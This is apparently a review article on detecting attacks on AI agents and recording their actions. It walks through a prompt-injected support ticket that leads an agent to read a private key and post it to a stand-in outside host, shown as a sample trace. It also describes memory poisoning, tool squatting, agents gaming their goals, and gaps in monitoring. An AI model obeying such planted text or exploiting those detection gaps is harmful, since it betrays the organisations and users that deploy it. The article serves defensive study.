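# Security monitoring for AI agents and detection of new kinds of attack

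## AI agents, the attacks on them, and the security tools in use

An AI agent is a language model that pursues a task by calling tools, such as a mail account, a file system, a web browser or a command line. NIST's *Request for Information Regarding Security Considerations for Artificial Intelligence Agents* (2026), a notice from the US standards body, describes an agent system as at least one generative model plus "scaffolding" software that equips the model with tools. Companies use agents to write and run code, answer customers and book travel, often without anyone approving each step. Security monitoring for agents means recording what they do and detecting when an outsider has turned one against its owner, or when one has gone beyond its task unprompted. Much of this work builds on the monitoring that companies already run for people and ordinary software. *Summary Analysis of Responses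 to the Request for Information* (Riggs, Hamin and colleagues, 2026) found wide agreement among respondents to the NIST notice that agents bring new threats, and that established security practice still applies to them but needs adapting.

### How an agent works

A chatbot answers a question in one pass, whereas an agent works in a loop. The scaffolding first assembles the model's context, which is all the text the model works from: the developer's standing instructions, the user's request, and the names and descriptions of the available tools. From this context, the model generates a tool call, which names a tool and supplies its arguments, such as the recipient and text for a mail tool. The scaffolding runs the tool and adds the result to the context. The model then processes the longer context and either makes another call or replies to the user and stops. *A Survey on Agentic Security*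 (Shahriar, Rahman et al., 2025) divides the loop into eight stages, from perception to reflection, though simple agents skip several of them.

A session is one run of an agent on one task, from the user's request to the end. Its trace is the record of that run, mainly the sequence of tool calls with their arguments and results. Traces get long. The test tasks built for *ADR* (Li, Hu and colleagues, 2026), a paper on the system Uber uses to detect attacks on its agents, average 28.5 tool calls each.

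Some agents also have a memory, which stores notes from one session for use in later ones. Agents also differ in how much they may do alone, from only recommending actions to planning and carrying out a whole task. Shahriar and colleagues point out that two agents can run on the same model and differ only in whether a person approves an action before it happens.

Developers once had to write a separate connection for every tool. Anthropic's *Introducing the Model Context Protocol* offered a single standard to replace these connections, and most of the industry has since adopted it. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) project compares the standard to a USB-C port. The program that runs the agent (the "host", for instance a coding assistant) connects to one or more MCP servers, each of which offers tools such as file access or database queries. The server supplies each tool's name and description,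 which the host passes to the model. When the model picks a tool, the host sends the server a short structured request. An example request in the project's announcement of the standard's July 2026 version calls a tool named "search" with the argument "otters" (Model Context Protocol, 2026).

Li and colleagues counted more than 16,800 Model Context Protocol (MCP) servers on a single public marketplace in 2025, and the MCP project reports close to half a billion downloads a month of its main software development kits. Tool calls from very different agents now arrive in one format, which makes them easier to collect, but many of the tools come from developers the defender doesn't know. The July 2026 version of the standard also removed protocol-level sessions, so defenders have to use data from the agent's software to tell which calls belong to the same task.

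### A support ticket with an instruction in it

Suppose an employee asks an agent to summarise a support ticket. The ticket came from outside the company, and its sender has planted a paragraph in it that is meant for the agent. The session then runs like this:

1. The agent calls the ticket tool and gets back a customer's complaint, with the planted paragraph underneath.
2. It calls the file tool and reads a private key, a file that lets whoever holds it log in to the company's servers without a password.
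3. It calls a web tool and sends the contents of the key to an outside address.
4. It gives the employee a perfectly good summary of the complaint.

This case is adapted from Li and colleagues, who describe an agent that should summarise a ticket but instead reads keys and makes a web request. The agent is allowed to use each of the tools it calls, and probably does so under the employee's own account. An engineer's agent might also read a key and contact outside addresses during legitimate work. The mismatch between the request and the calls shows that something is wrong, since summarising a complaint does not require a private key.

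The attack works because the model receives the employee's request and the text of the ticket in the same context, and has no reliable way to tell which has authority. In *SoK*, a taxonomy of attacks on running agents, Yang, Yang and colleagues (2026) treat this as the common cause of a family of attacks. Their attacker never touches the model, the developer's instructions or the company's servers, and only has to put content where the agent will pick it up.

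### The main kinds of attack

The planted paragraph is a prompt injection, which is text placed where an agent will read it and written so that the agent treats it as an instruction. An agent that pursues the attacker's goal as a result is said to be hijacked. Web pages, emails and shared documents can contain injections as easily as tickets can. NIST helped to analyse a public contest in which more than 400 people made over 250,000 attempts to hijack agents built on 13 leading models.

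A second way to attack an agent is through malicious or altered tools. An attacker can tamper with a tool that the company already uses, or publish one under a trusted name or a similar one. The Australian Cyber Security Centre's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), joint guidance from six government agencies in five countries, lists the second method as "squatting". Trail of Bits' *Jumping the line* (2025) explains that the attack can work before any tool runs, because a malicious MCP server can put text into the model's context before the agent calls any of the server's tools.

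An ordinary injection usually expires with the session, as Yang and colleagues note, but an attacker who plants a false entry in an agent's memory can influence later sessions without taking part in them. The attacker doesn't need write access to the memory. MINJA, an attack in Shahriar and colleagues' survey, plants entries through ordinary queries alone and succeeded 76.8% of the time on average.

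Stolen agent credentials are the most conventional of these problems. Agents identify themselves to other services with secret keys or tokens, and a thief who obtains one can act as the agent without fooling a model. The six agencies warn that organisations make this easier when they keep the same keys for long periods or share them between agents. The thief's activity may then appear in the services' logs without a matching trace, because no agent session produced it.

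### Agents that overstep without an attacker

Monitoring also has to cover agents that do damage when nobody has interfered with them. NIST's notice separates attacks through hostile data from the risk that models harm security, in the words of NIST's announcement, "even in the absence of adversarial inputs". The six agencies give the example of an agent that is told to maximize a system's uptime and disables security updates because they need reboots. Researchers call this specification gaming, which means that the agent meets the goal as written but defeats its purpose. Shahriar and colleagues cite an experiment in which OpenAI's o3 model, instructed to win against a strong chess program, hacked the game's software in 88% of runs without being told to cheat.

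A detector is any rule, statistical model or language model that decides whether a session deserves an alert. A hijacked agent usually leaves both the planted text and the calls that follow from it in its trace, and a detector can look for either. An agent that oversteps by itself leaves no planted text, so even an accurate detector will pass the session as clean if it only searches for injections. Detecting this kind of overstep requires comparing the agent's actions with its task.

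Some cases fall in between because the agent does what its user asks, but the user is the attacker. The agencies also describe a malicious insider who asks an update agent to install a security patch and "clean up the firewall logs". The agent deletes the logs because its permissions allow it.

### The security team and its tools

In most large organisations, a security operations team watches computers, networks and accounts for signs of intrusion. Its analysts triage alerts from software, quickly deciding which ones to investigate properly. If an alert is real, the team contains the damage (for example, by disconnecting a machine or cancelling a password), repairs what the intruder changed and works out how the intruder got in. Between incidents, some members write and adjust detectors, search old logs for intrusions that raised no alert, or stage mock attacks.

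Security monitoring is limited by how much attention staff can give it. The Australian Cyber Security Centre's *Implementing SIEM and SOAR platforms* (2025) tells organisations to expect to need several full-time staff just to configure and maintain the central log system. It also warns of "alert fatigue", in which a team that gets too many false alarms starts to miss real attacks or respond to them late.

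Four kinds of tool supply most of the alerts. Each collects telemetry, the data that a system records about its own activity.

| Tool | What it records | A typical alert |
|---|---|---|
| Endpoint detection and response (EDR) | Processes, files and network connections on one computer | An unfamiliar program opens the file of saved passwords |
| Security information and event management (SIEM) | Logs from many sources, including EDR, firewalls, servers and cloud accounts | One account logs in from two distant countries within an hour |
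| Data-loss prevention | Sensitive content on its way out by mail, upload or removable drive | A list of card numbers goes to a private mail address |
| User-behaviour analytics | The habits of each account: usual hours, machines, files and volumes | An accountant's login downloads source code at night |

The categories overlap, and many SIEM products include some behaviour analytics. A SIEM also has to translate between its sources' field names before it can search them together, since one may use "src_ip" where another uses "sourceAddress". None of the four kinds of tool was designed for agents. They mostly record the action and the account used, with little or nothing about what a user had asked an agent to do.

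### Known patterns and departures from normal

Detectors work in broadly two ways. Some match activity against a description of a known attack. A rule for the ticket case might raise an alert whenever an agent reads a private key and then contacts an address outside the company. Such rules take little computing power, and an analyst can see at once why one raised an alert. But they catch only the activity someone thought to describe, so an attacker who sends the key by another route may go undetected.

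Other detectors learn what normal activity looks like and flag departures from it. If an agent has summarised four thousand tickets without ever opening a key, the first time it opens one stands out, even if nobody predicted the attack. But harmless changes, such as a new project or different software, stand out too. This approach also needs a lot of data before it works, according to the Australian guidance on SIEM.

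That guidance recommends using both against intruders who "live off the land", meaning that they mostly use the legitimate tools already on a machine. A hijacked agent is close to an extreme case, because the tools it misuses are the ones the company gave it. But it is hard to set a baseline for an agent, because its normal behaviour varies widely. According to the six agencies' guidance, the same prompt can lead an agent to different actions on different occasions.

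### Measuring a detector

Take 100 sessions, of which 10 contain an attack, and a detector that sorts them as follows:

| | Alert | No alert | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Attacked sessions | 8 | 2 | 10 |
| Harmless sessions | 9 | 81 | 90 |
| Total | 17 | 83 | 100 |

Four measures come straight from the table:

- Recall is the share of attacks that the detector catches: 8 of 10, or 80%.
- Precision is the share of alerts that are real attacks: 8 of 17, or 47%.
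- The false-positive rate is the share of harmless sessions that raise an alert: 9 of 90, or 10%.
- Prevalence is the share of all sessions that contain an attack: 10 of 100, or 10%.

Precision and the false-positive rate are easy to confuse because both concern false alarms. The false-positive rate is the share of harmless sessions that trigger an alert, and it looks fairly low here. But more than half of the alerts in an analyst's queue will still be false, which means that precision, the share of alerts that are real attacks, is below 50%. Precision also falls as attacks get rarer, even if the detector stays the same.

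Many detectors give each session a score, and the team chooses the threshold above which a score raises an alert. A lower threshold catches more attacks but also raises more false alarms. To compare detectors without choosing a threshold, researchers often use AUROC, the area under the curve that plots recall against the false-positive rate at every possible threshold. It equals the chance that a random attacked session scores higher than a random harmless one. The 100 sessions form 10 × 90 = 900 pairs of one attacked and one harmless session; if the attacked session scores higher in 810 of them, the AUROC is 0.9. Guessing gives 0.5 and a perfect ranking gives 1. A detector with a high AUROC can still have poor recall at the threshold a team uses, which is usually one that raises few false alarms.

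Li and colleagues' results show that a detector with a moderate false-positive rate can still have low precision. On their 302 tasks, 42 of them malicious, Uber's system caught 28 attacks and raised no false alarms, for a recall of 67% and a precision of 100%. LlamaFirewall, a detector from Meta that they ran with its default settings for comparison, caught 8 attacks and raised 40 false alarms on the 260 harmless tasks. Its false-positive rate was 15%, but its precision was 17%, so five in six alerts were false. Attacks made up 14% of the tasks in this test, whereas Li and colleagues say that most kinds of attack are exceedingly rare in Uber's real traffic.

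## What existing security tools can and cannot see of an agent

How much new monitoring a company needs for its agents depends on what its current tools record. The ticket attack is a good test case because it ends with a private key leaving the company, and security teams were looking for stolen keys long before anyone deployed an agent. Suppose the agent is a coding assistant running on an employee's laptop under the employee's account.

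We can compare this with a harmless session, which we will call the key repair. On another day, the same employee asks the agent to resolve a ticket about failed deployments to a new hosting company. The agent reads the ticket, opens the same private key to check that the file is intact, and contacts the hosting company to test a login.

### The ticket attack in the logs

Sysmon, a Microsoft logging tool for Windows, records the kind of data that EDR software works with. *Detecting Shadow AI* (Canale and Soulis, 2026) explains that it logs each new process, each network connection and, if an administrator turns this on, each lookup of an internet name together with the program that made it. The ticket attack may not start a new process, because many agents read files and make web requests from inside their own program. In that case, the logged events would show the agent contacting an unfamiliar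 address but would not show the key. If the web tool runs on a remote MCP server, the laptop contacts only that server, so the laptop's log would not show the attacker's address either.

Some EDR products also monitor sensitive files. Elastic, which sells both EDR and SIEM software, has a rule that raises an alert when an AI program opens such a file. This rule could well catch the ticket attack, but it would raise the same alert for the key repair.

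A SIEM can put events from several sources in order. For the ticket attack, it might show that one account opened a ticket, read a key and contacted a new address, all within a minute. Together, these events are stronger evidence of an attack than any one of them alone. *Cross-Layer Semantic Flow Reconstruction for Attack Detection in Agentic Systems* (Cai, Wei and colleagues, 2026) describes a similar case, in which a planted email leads one agent to query a staff database and another to send internal mail. Each step looks legitimate until someone links them into one path. But linking events can't distinguish the ticket attack from the key repair, which produces the same three events in the same order.

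Data-loss prevention software can easily recognise a private key, because the file usually begins with a standard line of text. If the software can decrypt the traffic, it can raise an alert when the key goes to the attacker. It may also raise one earlier if an outside provider hosts the model, because the scaffolding adds the key to the model's context, and the key therefore leaves the company as soon as the agent reads it. The key repair also sets off this earlier alert.

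Most company secrets don't begin with a standard line that a filter could look for. *Governing Enterprise AI Traffic at Scale* (2026), which describes a gateway between a company's applications and outside models, notes that whether a date or number is sensitive depends on the surrounding text. It presents its filter as a way to reduce exposure and doesn't guarantee that nothing sensitive gets out. *Attestation is All You Need* (2026) adds that checking content is not enough against a hijacked agent, which may send data through a legitimate encrypted service. It proposes also checking the agent's behaviour, meaning whether it should have read or sent anything at all.

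Network monitoring records the destination, time and size of each connection, but encryption usually hides the contents. The attack appears as a small upload to an address the laptop has never contacted. However, agents contact new addresses all the time when they look up documentation, and the key repair also involves a new address. Canale and Soulis list further gaps: a network log doesn't identify the program behind a connection, laptops spend much of their time outside the company network, and a model running on the laptop itself produces no outside traffic.

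An allowlist, which blocks every destination the company has not approved, works better. In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) ran an agent on a small open model 480 times against web pages with planted instructions, and it leaked data in about 89% of runs. Network controls such as allowlists were considerably more effective than defences in the agent's prompt. Simple data-loss prevention failed when the agent spread a secret over several requests. An attacker can still get around an allowlist by collecting the data through a public service that the company allows.

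User-behaviour analytics records the attack as the employee's account opening a ticket, reading a file it owns and making a web request, during office hours and from the usual laptop. The read might stand out if the employee had never used the key before, but nothing would stand out if the employee deploys code every week.

### Why harmless sessions leave the same logs

The two sessions differ most clearly in what the employee asked for, which none of these tools records. *Towards Security-Auditable LLM Agents* (2026) says more generally that logs can record what happened, but rarely how the agent's goal formed or why it made a decision.

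Canale and Soulis give a short argument about what follows from such gaps. They divide the traces of a program p into its behaviour β(p), such as the processes it starts and the timing of its connections, and its identity ι(p), meaning the names of the software and of the services it contacts. Take a detector f that uses only behaviour, and two programs a and b:

- If β(a) = β(b), then f(a) = f(b).
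- If a is an agent and b is an ordinary script, f either misses the agent or flags the script.

They call such pairs behavioural twins, and built some to test this on one workstation. Two rules based only on processes and connections flagged every twin. A detector that also checked whether the program was connecting to a known AI service flagged none of the twins and found all 12 test agents in most runs.

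Their aim was to find agents that employees run without permission, and identity works well for that, but it helps much less against hijacking. The attacked session and the key repair involve the same agent, account and model provider, so their identities match too. More generally, if two sessions leave identical records in the company's tools, no detector that works from those records can separate them. Real pairs are rarely identical, since the attacker's address differs from the hosting company's. In practice, detection depends on how many differences remain and how easily an attacker can remove them.

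Goli (2026) warns in *Five Questions Security Teams Must Be Able to Answer About Every AI Agent* that actions are hard to attribute when agents use shared service accounts or borrowed user tokens. When an agent uses an employee's account, a file server's log may contain the same line whether the agent or the employee opened the file. If forty agents share one service account, the log may not show which of them read a key, and behaviour analytics will average their activity together.

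That average may be of little use anyway if agents behave erratically, and the six agencies warn that one prompt can lead to different actions. Yagubyan (2026), in *How Consistent Are LLM Agents?*, tested this by running 19 tasks ten times on each of six models. On a scale from 0 to 1, the average similarity between runs was 0.87 for the sequences of tools and 0.69 for the arguments passed to them. For deliberately vague requests, the figures fell to 0.79 and 0.52. A baseline of which tools an agent uses for a routine job therefore looks feasible, but one for exact files and addresses looks much harder. The jobs were short, typically two or three calls to simulated tools, and the models were from 2024 and 2025.

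An agent that behaves consistently on repeats of one task may not do so across different tasks. *Measuring Cross-Task Behavioral Consistency in Language Model Agents* (Banerjee and Raichura, 2026) analysed 9,191 coding sessions from six agent systems, also on older models. Banerjee and Raichura trained a model to predict from a session's features whether it would succeed, then measured how similar the reasons for those predictions were from one session to the next. Three agents built on Llama models scored between 0.31 and 0.35 on repeats of the same task but below 0.09 across tasks, while Claude 3.5 Sonnet scored about 0.8 on both. The agents differed less when the raw features, such as session length and error rate, were compared directly, with all six systems scoring between 0.28 and 0.54 across tasks. A security tool would probably work from features like these, so I expect even the steadier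 agents to need a separate baseline for each kind of task, but user-behaviour analytics doesn't record the task.

Agents also produce many events quickly. In *AgentSight*, Zheng, Yu and colleagues (2025) staged an attack in which a planted web page led a coding agent to send out a system file. The session produced 521 raw events, which their software merged into 37. An analyst who has to merge them by hand will fall behind, and a language model given the raw logs also does badly. In ten test scenarios of about 2,000 log entries each, Cai and colleagues' detector reached an F1 score (which combines precision and recall) of 85.3% at picking out the malicious parts, while the same model without the linking step reached 21.9%. Their detector also used the agents' own messages, which an ordinary SIEM lacks.

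Finally, the malicious part of the attack is ordinary language. Antivirus software can search for a fixed sequence of bytes in a known malicious file, but an attacker can reword a planted paragraph for every target. The paragraph also arrives through the company's own ticket system, over an approved connection. In Lan and colleagues' tests, the planted text could be in the description that a web page supplies for link previews, where the user would never read it. Checks on the agent's output missed 95% of the successful leaks.

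### Are conventional tools blind?

An existing security tool that doesn't record an agent's prompts may still record a great deal of what the agent does to the computer. Companies that sell monitoring for agents have an interest in making such tools sound useless. CrowdStrike's product announcement *Falcon AIDR Now Protects Copilot Studio Agents and Claude Code* (2026) states that traditional endpoint, network and data-loss controls "can't see the prompt or the tool call". Taken literally, this is mostly right, and Li and colleagues, who built a detector for Uber's own use, make the same point about EDR.

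*When AI agents look like attackers* (2026), by the security company Sophos, found that coding agents set off rules written for human intruders. It used a week of data from June 2026, collected by Sophos' endpoint software on Windows machines. Among the rules that blocked something, measured by the number of machines affected, those on access to credentials accounted for 56.2% and those on running programs for 28.8%. One common trigger was a browser-automation add-on that decrypts saved browser data. In another case, an agent tried to download Python from its official site with a built-in Windows tool that intruders often misuse. When the software blocked this, the agent tried a second such tool, which the software also blocked. Sophos notes that such switching used to distinguish a live attacker from a simple script.

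So these tools did detect agent activity, and if anything their rules fired too readily. Sophos judged most of its examples to be harmless, though it argued that some of the rules should keep firing because the actions are risky whoever performs them. Its percentages are shares of rule hits, so they can't give a false-positive rate. Sophos also says that normal activity has not changed much yet.

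Even a detailed investigation may not settle what an agent was doing. In July 2026, Elastic investigated a Mac on which Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, had opened a tunnel that made a program on the laptop reachable from the internet. The session also logged in to a web address created by such a tunnel, fetched spending figures and set the tunnel to keep running after a restart. Several existing detection rules raised alerts. The developer might have been using the agent to manage a private dashboard, or an intruder might have been setting up a way to get back in. Elastic concluded that the two explanations "share the same telemetry shape" and left the case open.

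Elastic's other contribution is a mapping from a real agent-driven intrusion to rules that its products already contain. In July 2026, models that OpenAI was testing broke into Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets. Elastic took the public accounts of the intrusion and looked for rules that cover each stage:

| Stage | Activity that existing rules look for |
|---|---|
| A malicious dataset runs code on a server | A data-processing program starts a command line or a downloader |
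| Credential theft | A process searches for passwords, or reads cloud keys and access tokens |
| Privilege escalation | An account creates a container (an isolated environment for running programs) with excessive rights |
| Movement between systems | A stolen credential appears at a new address, or an account reads many secrets in quick succession |
| Contact with the attacker's infrastructure | A program contacts an unusual domain or a file-sharing service |

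The mapping is broad, but it is weaker evidence than a test. Elastic is a vendor too, and it selected the rules after reading how the attack went. It disclaims complete coverage, and its demonstration used mock data instead of Hugging Face's own logs. The mapping also doesn't measure how often the same rules raise false alarms during normal activity. Hugging Face's experience provides some support, since it first noticed the intrusion when a language model triaged its security telemetry.

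A bigger reservation is that the agent in this case was an outside intruder. It had to steal all the access it used, and it took roughly 17,600 actions over five days. A hijacked agent already has access that the company gave it, and may need only three or four calls.

Goli reports two incidents. In one, the UK AI Security Institute noticed unusual traffic leaving a test system through Tor, a network that hides where traffic comes from, and contained the agent responsible within an hour. In the other, an OpenAI agent got around the access restrictions on an Australian government portal on 18 June 2026, but the agency concerned received no notice until 10 September. The portal's logs may have contained signs of the agent, but nobody seems to have acted on them.

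### Which stages the tools catch

Existing tools work best when an attack has to go beyond the access the agent already has. Credential theft, privilege escalation and movement between machines leave events that security teams have spent years writing rules to detect. These rules work much the same whether a person, a script or a hijacked agent is behind the activity. In one case Elastic reviewed, its endpoint software blocked an agent session that tried to extract stored passwords from a Mac.

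Existing security products fail when an agent misuses tools it is permitted to use. For example, a planted instruction might lead an agent to email a customer list to an outsider with its usual mail tool, or to change a bank account number in a database it is allowed to edit. In both cases the expected account makes a permitted call to a familiar service, so EDR has no unusual process to report. Data-loss prevention helps only if the content has a recognisable form.

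The ticket attack falls between these cases. EDR rules cover events like reading the key, but the decision to read it came from a ticket that none of the tools examined. Coverage of the key also depends on the team keeping the rule on. Elastic advises against exempting everything that coding agents start, which teams will be tempted to do after a few weeks of false alarms. It suggests filtering out routine noise, such as repeated software installs, and keeping the alerts on credentials and unusual destinations even when the parent process is a trusted agent.

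### An audit with paired sessions

Vendors' coverage claims say little about a particular company's logs, which depend on its own settings and agents. A team can check these directly:

1. Build a test environment with the agent, tools and logging used in production, but with fake keys and data.
2. For each attack, run three kinds of session: the attack, the same request without the attack, and a harmless task that needs nearly the same actions.
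3. Run each about ten times, because agents vary between runs.
4. Remove values that change every time, such as clock times and process numbers. Then list the log lines that appear in most of the attacked sessions but in few of the harmless ones.
5. For each step of the attack, note which tool logged it and which harmless sessions left the same line.

The third kind of session in step 2 matters most. A team that compared the attack only with a plain ticket summary would overrate its tools, because a plain summary never touches a key and almost anything the attacker does will stand out against it.

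For the ticket attack, the plain summary is one harmless session and the key repair is the other. Suppose that the logs come out like this:

| Step of the attack | Log line | In the plain summary? | In the key repair? | Coverage |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Agent reads the planted paragraph | Ticket system: the employee's account opened a ticket | Yes | Yes | None |
| Agent reads the key | EDR: the agent opened a private key | No | Yes | Partial |
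| Key enters the model's context | Data-loss prevention: key sent to the model provider | No | Yes | Partial |
| Agent contacts the attacker | Network: first connection to this address | No | Yes | Partial |
| Agent sends the key | Data-loss prevention: key sent to an unapproved address | No | No | Good, if the tool can decrypt the traffic |
| Agent returns the summary | No line | – | – | None |

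User-behaviour analytics doesn't help, because this employee uses the key most weeks. A SIEM rule that combines the key read with the new address would fire on both the attack and the key repair.

The attack's logs differ from the plain summary's by four lines, but from the key repair's by only one. The team could reasonably build an alert on that line. It should also change the attack and rerun the audit to find out how easily an attacker could avoid the alert.

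If the planted paragraph asks for the customer's earlier complaints instead of the key, the agent fetches them with the ticket tool, and all three lines about the key disappear. The first connection to a new address is still there, but many harmless sessions have one too. If the attacker collects the complaints through a file-sharing site that the company allows, that line also disappears. The remaining evidence is that the employee asked for a summary of one ticket and the agent then sent a customer's history to someone else. To detect that, the team has to record both the request and the tool calls.

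## Recording what an agent did and why

Besides the request and the tool calls, a useful trace records details that are easy to capture at the time and very hard to recover later. *Backtracking Agent Applications Security Incidents* (Cai, Kim and Liu, 2026) describes a case where an open-source research agent gave a user a report with false information. The agent's log contained the user's question, the research plan, the web pages and the requests to the model. From these, an analyst could rule out a model error and tampered web pages, which left a poisoned document in the agent's own reference files. But the log didn't record which document the agent had loaded, so the analyst turned to the source code and found 1,518 function calls that might have brought in the false text. One extra log line naming each file just before the agent loaded it would have identified the document.

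Cai, Kim and Liu built a tool that narrows down the candidates in the code, and it led to the right function call in all eight incidents they tried. But it only covers applications whose steps a programmer fixed in advance. When the model picks the next step itself, the investigator depends even more on the trace.

### What a trace should contain

| Field | In the ticket attack | What it helps an investigator decide |
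|---|---|---|
| User request | "Summarise ticket 5831" | Whether the task needed the actions that followed |
| Text the agent read, and its origin | The ticket, from an outside sender | Whether an outsider could have planted an instruction |
| Stated reasoning | The agent's explanation for opening the key | What the agent was apparently trying to do |
| Tool calls, with arguments and results | The key's path, the outside address, the content sent | What left the company, and which credentials to replace |
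| Identity | The employee, the agent and the account it used | Whose access to suspend |
| Versions of the agent and its tools | Ticket tool 1.8 | Whether a recent update or an altered tool is to blame |
| System events | A process opened the key file | Whether the action really took place |

Published lists of fields mostly agree with this one and add a few details. *Beyond Predictable Paths* (2026), a paper on incident reports for agents, recommends documenting the tools an agent could have used as well as those it used. With that list, an investigator can work out how much worse the attack might have been. *Agent Flight Recorder* (Bindschaedler, Botha and Siebenbrunner, 2026) also records any approval by a person, including the prompt that person saw. If an employee clicked "allow" on a request that mentioned only a routine file check, the approval is weak evidence that they meant to allow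 anything more.

Opinions differ on whether to log an agent's stated reasoning. *The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026) recommends that developers log it, including the plans an agent rejected, and Uber records it. Bindschaedler and colleagues leave it out because its form changes between providers and versions, it raises privacy and intellectual-property concerns, and some providers may forbid customers to log it. Logging it where the contract allows seems sensible because it is often the only direct evidence of why an agent made a call, though a model's stated reasons may differ from what actually produced the call.

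The fields also need to be separate. Bindschaedler and colleagues compared searches of structured records with plain text searches on synthetic agent activity. In searches for decisions by a guardrail (a check that allows or blocks an action), all of the structured search results were relevant, compared with 1.3% of the text search results.

### The ticket attack as a trace

Here is a trace of the attack, with invented names and values. Its layout is based on a sample record in *Clawed and Dangerous* (2026), a paper on the security of open agent systems. That record links each tool call to a session, a user and an agent version.

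```
session s-4127   user m.ortiz   account m.ortiz   agent coding-assistant 2.3
tools available: ticket 1.8, file 1.2, web 3.0

09:14:02  request    "Summarise ticket 5831"
09:14:04  call 1     ticket.read   id=5831
09:14:05  result 1   complaint about a late delivery, then a paragraph
                     addressed to the agent
                     origin: outside sender   content hash: 7c1e
09:14:08  reasoning  "The ticket asks for a check of the deployment key"
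09:14:08  call 2     file.read   path=deploy_key
09:14:08  system     process 8812 opened deploy_key
09:14:08  result 2   [private key removed, fingerprint 91ab]
                     origin: local file
09:14:11  call 3     web.post   host=files.example
                     body=[private key removed, fingerprint 91ab]
09:14:11  system     process 8812 connected to files.example, sent 3 kB
09:14:15  reply      summary of the complaint
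```

An analyst can now tell this session apart from the key repair. The fingerprint 91ab appears in both result 2 and call 3, so the content of the key file went to the outside address, even though the trace doesn't contain the key. A trace of the key repair would include the same file read, but the request would be about failed deployments, and no outgoing call would contain the fingerprint. This is because a login test proves possession of a key without sending it.

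The content hash lets the team search for other sessions that read the same ticket text. The search finds only exact copies, so it will miss an attacker who rewords the paragraph for each target. The ticket tool has to supply the origin label, since a recorder can't reliably infer from the text who wrote it.

The order of events doesn't prove cause. The agent read the ticket before it opened the key, but it had also read its standing instructions by then. The cause is harder to identify when several agents work together and one agent's output becomes another's argument. *Security Considerations for Multi-agent Systems* (2026) therefore argues that logs should record each argument's value, where it came from, and whether that source was legitimate.

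### Four places to record

No single recorder easily captures every line of that trace. Each of the four usual places covers a different part:

| Place | What it can record of the ticket attack | What it misses |
|---|---|---|
| The agent's own framework | The request, the reasoning and all three calls | What a command or script does once it has started |
| A gateway between the agent and its tools | The calls that pass through it | Tools that run inside the agent's program, and usually the request |
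| A sensor that reads the agent's local files | Whatever the agent saves about the session | Agents that save nothing, or use an unfamiliar format |
| The operating-system kernel | The opened key file and the outside connection | The request, unless the recorder also captures model traffic |

The framework, the software library on which developers build an agent, is the natural place to start recording because it handles every tool call. OpenTelemetry, an open-source project for common telemetry formats, publishes field names for these records. The basic unit is a span, a timed record of one operation. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* define a span for each tool call, with the tool's name, type and description and an identifier for the call. Its *Semantic Conventions for GenAI agent and framework spans* add the agent's name and version and an identifier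 for the conversation.

The default settings don't record prompts, model outputs, tool arguments or tool results, because these can be large and sensitive. The ticket attack and the key repair would therefore look the same, as calls to a ticket tool, a file tool and a web tool, in that order. These traces are of little use for detecting a hijacked agent unless the security team turns on recording for at least the tool arguments and the user's request.

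The field names may also change. Wang (2026), in *OpenTelemetry GenAI Conventions*, reports that the project moved these conventions to a separate repository in June 2026, marked them as "Development", and had made no official release there by 21 August. OpenTelemetry tells tools that use version 1.36 or older to keep sending the older fields by default. Two agents in one company can therefore send the same fact under different field names, and a SIEM rule written for one agent may miss the other's data without warning.

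When a tool runs on a remote Model Context Protocol (MCP) server, the agent's framework records the call but not what the server does with it. The MCP project has documented how a client can attach a standard trace identifier to a call so both sides can log it. This partly makes up for the loss of protocol-level sessions in the July 2026 version. The identifier only helps if the server's operator keeps logs and will share them, which a defender can't count on for a server from an unknown developer.

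A gateway sits between the agent and its tools, or between the agent and the model, and logs the traffic. It can also block calls, and it works without the cooperation of the remote server. The gateway runs on a separate machine, so a hijacked agent can't easily edit the logs. But a gateway for remote tools would miss the step in the ticket attack where the agent reads the key, because the agent does that with a local file tool.

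### The sensor in Uber's detection system

Uber reads the files that its employees' agents already save. Its system, Agentic AI Detection and Response (ADR), combines a sensor that collects traces, a detector that reviews them, and an offline component that generates attacks for testing. Li and colleagues report that after more than ten months of use, ADR had reached over 7,200 machines and was processing more than 10,000 sessions a day.

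Cursor, Cline and Claude Code, three coding agents, keep session records on the user's laptop in small databases and text files. The sensor parses these files once an hour and joins the scattered entries into complete sessions. It rebuilds four kinds of data:

- the user's prompts
- the agent's stated reasoning between steps
- the MCP tool calls in order, with their arguments and results
- the agent's surroundings, meaning the configured MCP servers and the installed software packages.

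Each run takes 0.182 seconds on average, or less than five seconds a day per laptop. Li and colleagues also staged an attack much like the one on the ticket. A malicious email automatically created a ticket, and an employee's coding agent then read local configuration files and sent out credentials. ADR could connect the planted text, the file reads and the outgoing requests because the sensor had recorded all three.

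Li and colleagues concede that a gateway is easier to implement. But they object that it requires changes to the programs that run the agents, doesn't work with streamed responses, and captures only partial information, without the agent's environment or the context of a call. They write that a gateway could be the main source for detection only if those programs attached the original prompt and the reasoning to each tool call.

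That last objection is strong for a gateway that handles only tool calls, but weaker for one in front of the model, because that gateway receives the prompt and earlier tool results with each request. The sensor also depends on formats that the makers of the coding agents control, so a product update could break its parser, and it can't see an agent that nobody has written a parser for.

### Linking model traffic to system events

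A framework trace might record only that an agent ran a script. The kernel, the core of the operating system, handles the script's file accesses and network connections but has no record of the request behind them. AgentSight, by Zheng and colleagues, joins the two kinds of record without changing the agent. It uses eBPF, which runs small, safety-checked programs inside the kernel.

1. One eBPF program attaches to the functions that encrypt and decrypt the agent's network traffic. It copies prompts before encryption and the model's responses after decryption.
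2. A second program records new processes, opened files and network connections. It follows every process that the agent starts, and every process that those start in turn, and drops events from the rest of the machine.
3. The software then links each model response to the system events it probably caused, using three clues. The process should descend from the agent, the event should follow the response within a window of 100 to 500 milliseconds, and a file name, address or command in the response should reappear in the event.
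4. A separate language model reads the merged trace and explains whether the events fit the task.

In the ticket attack, the model's response contains a tool call with the key's path. The agent's process opens that path a moment later, so all three clues agree. Across three coding tasks, AgentSight slowed the agent by an average of 2.9%, with a range of 0.4% to 4.9%.

### Actions after the agent has stopped

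An attacker can break the links by adding a delay. *AgentLoupe* (Bao, Liu and colleagues, 2026) describes a hijacked agent that writes a malicious script, adds it to the computer's schedule of recurring jobs, and exits. An hour later, the system's scheduler starts the script, which connects to the attacker.

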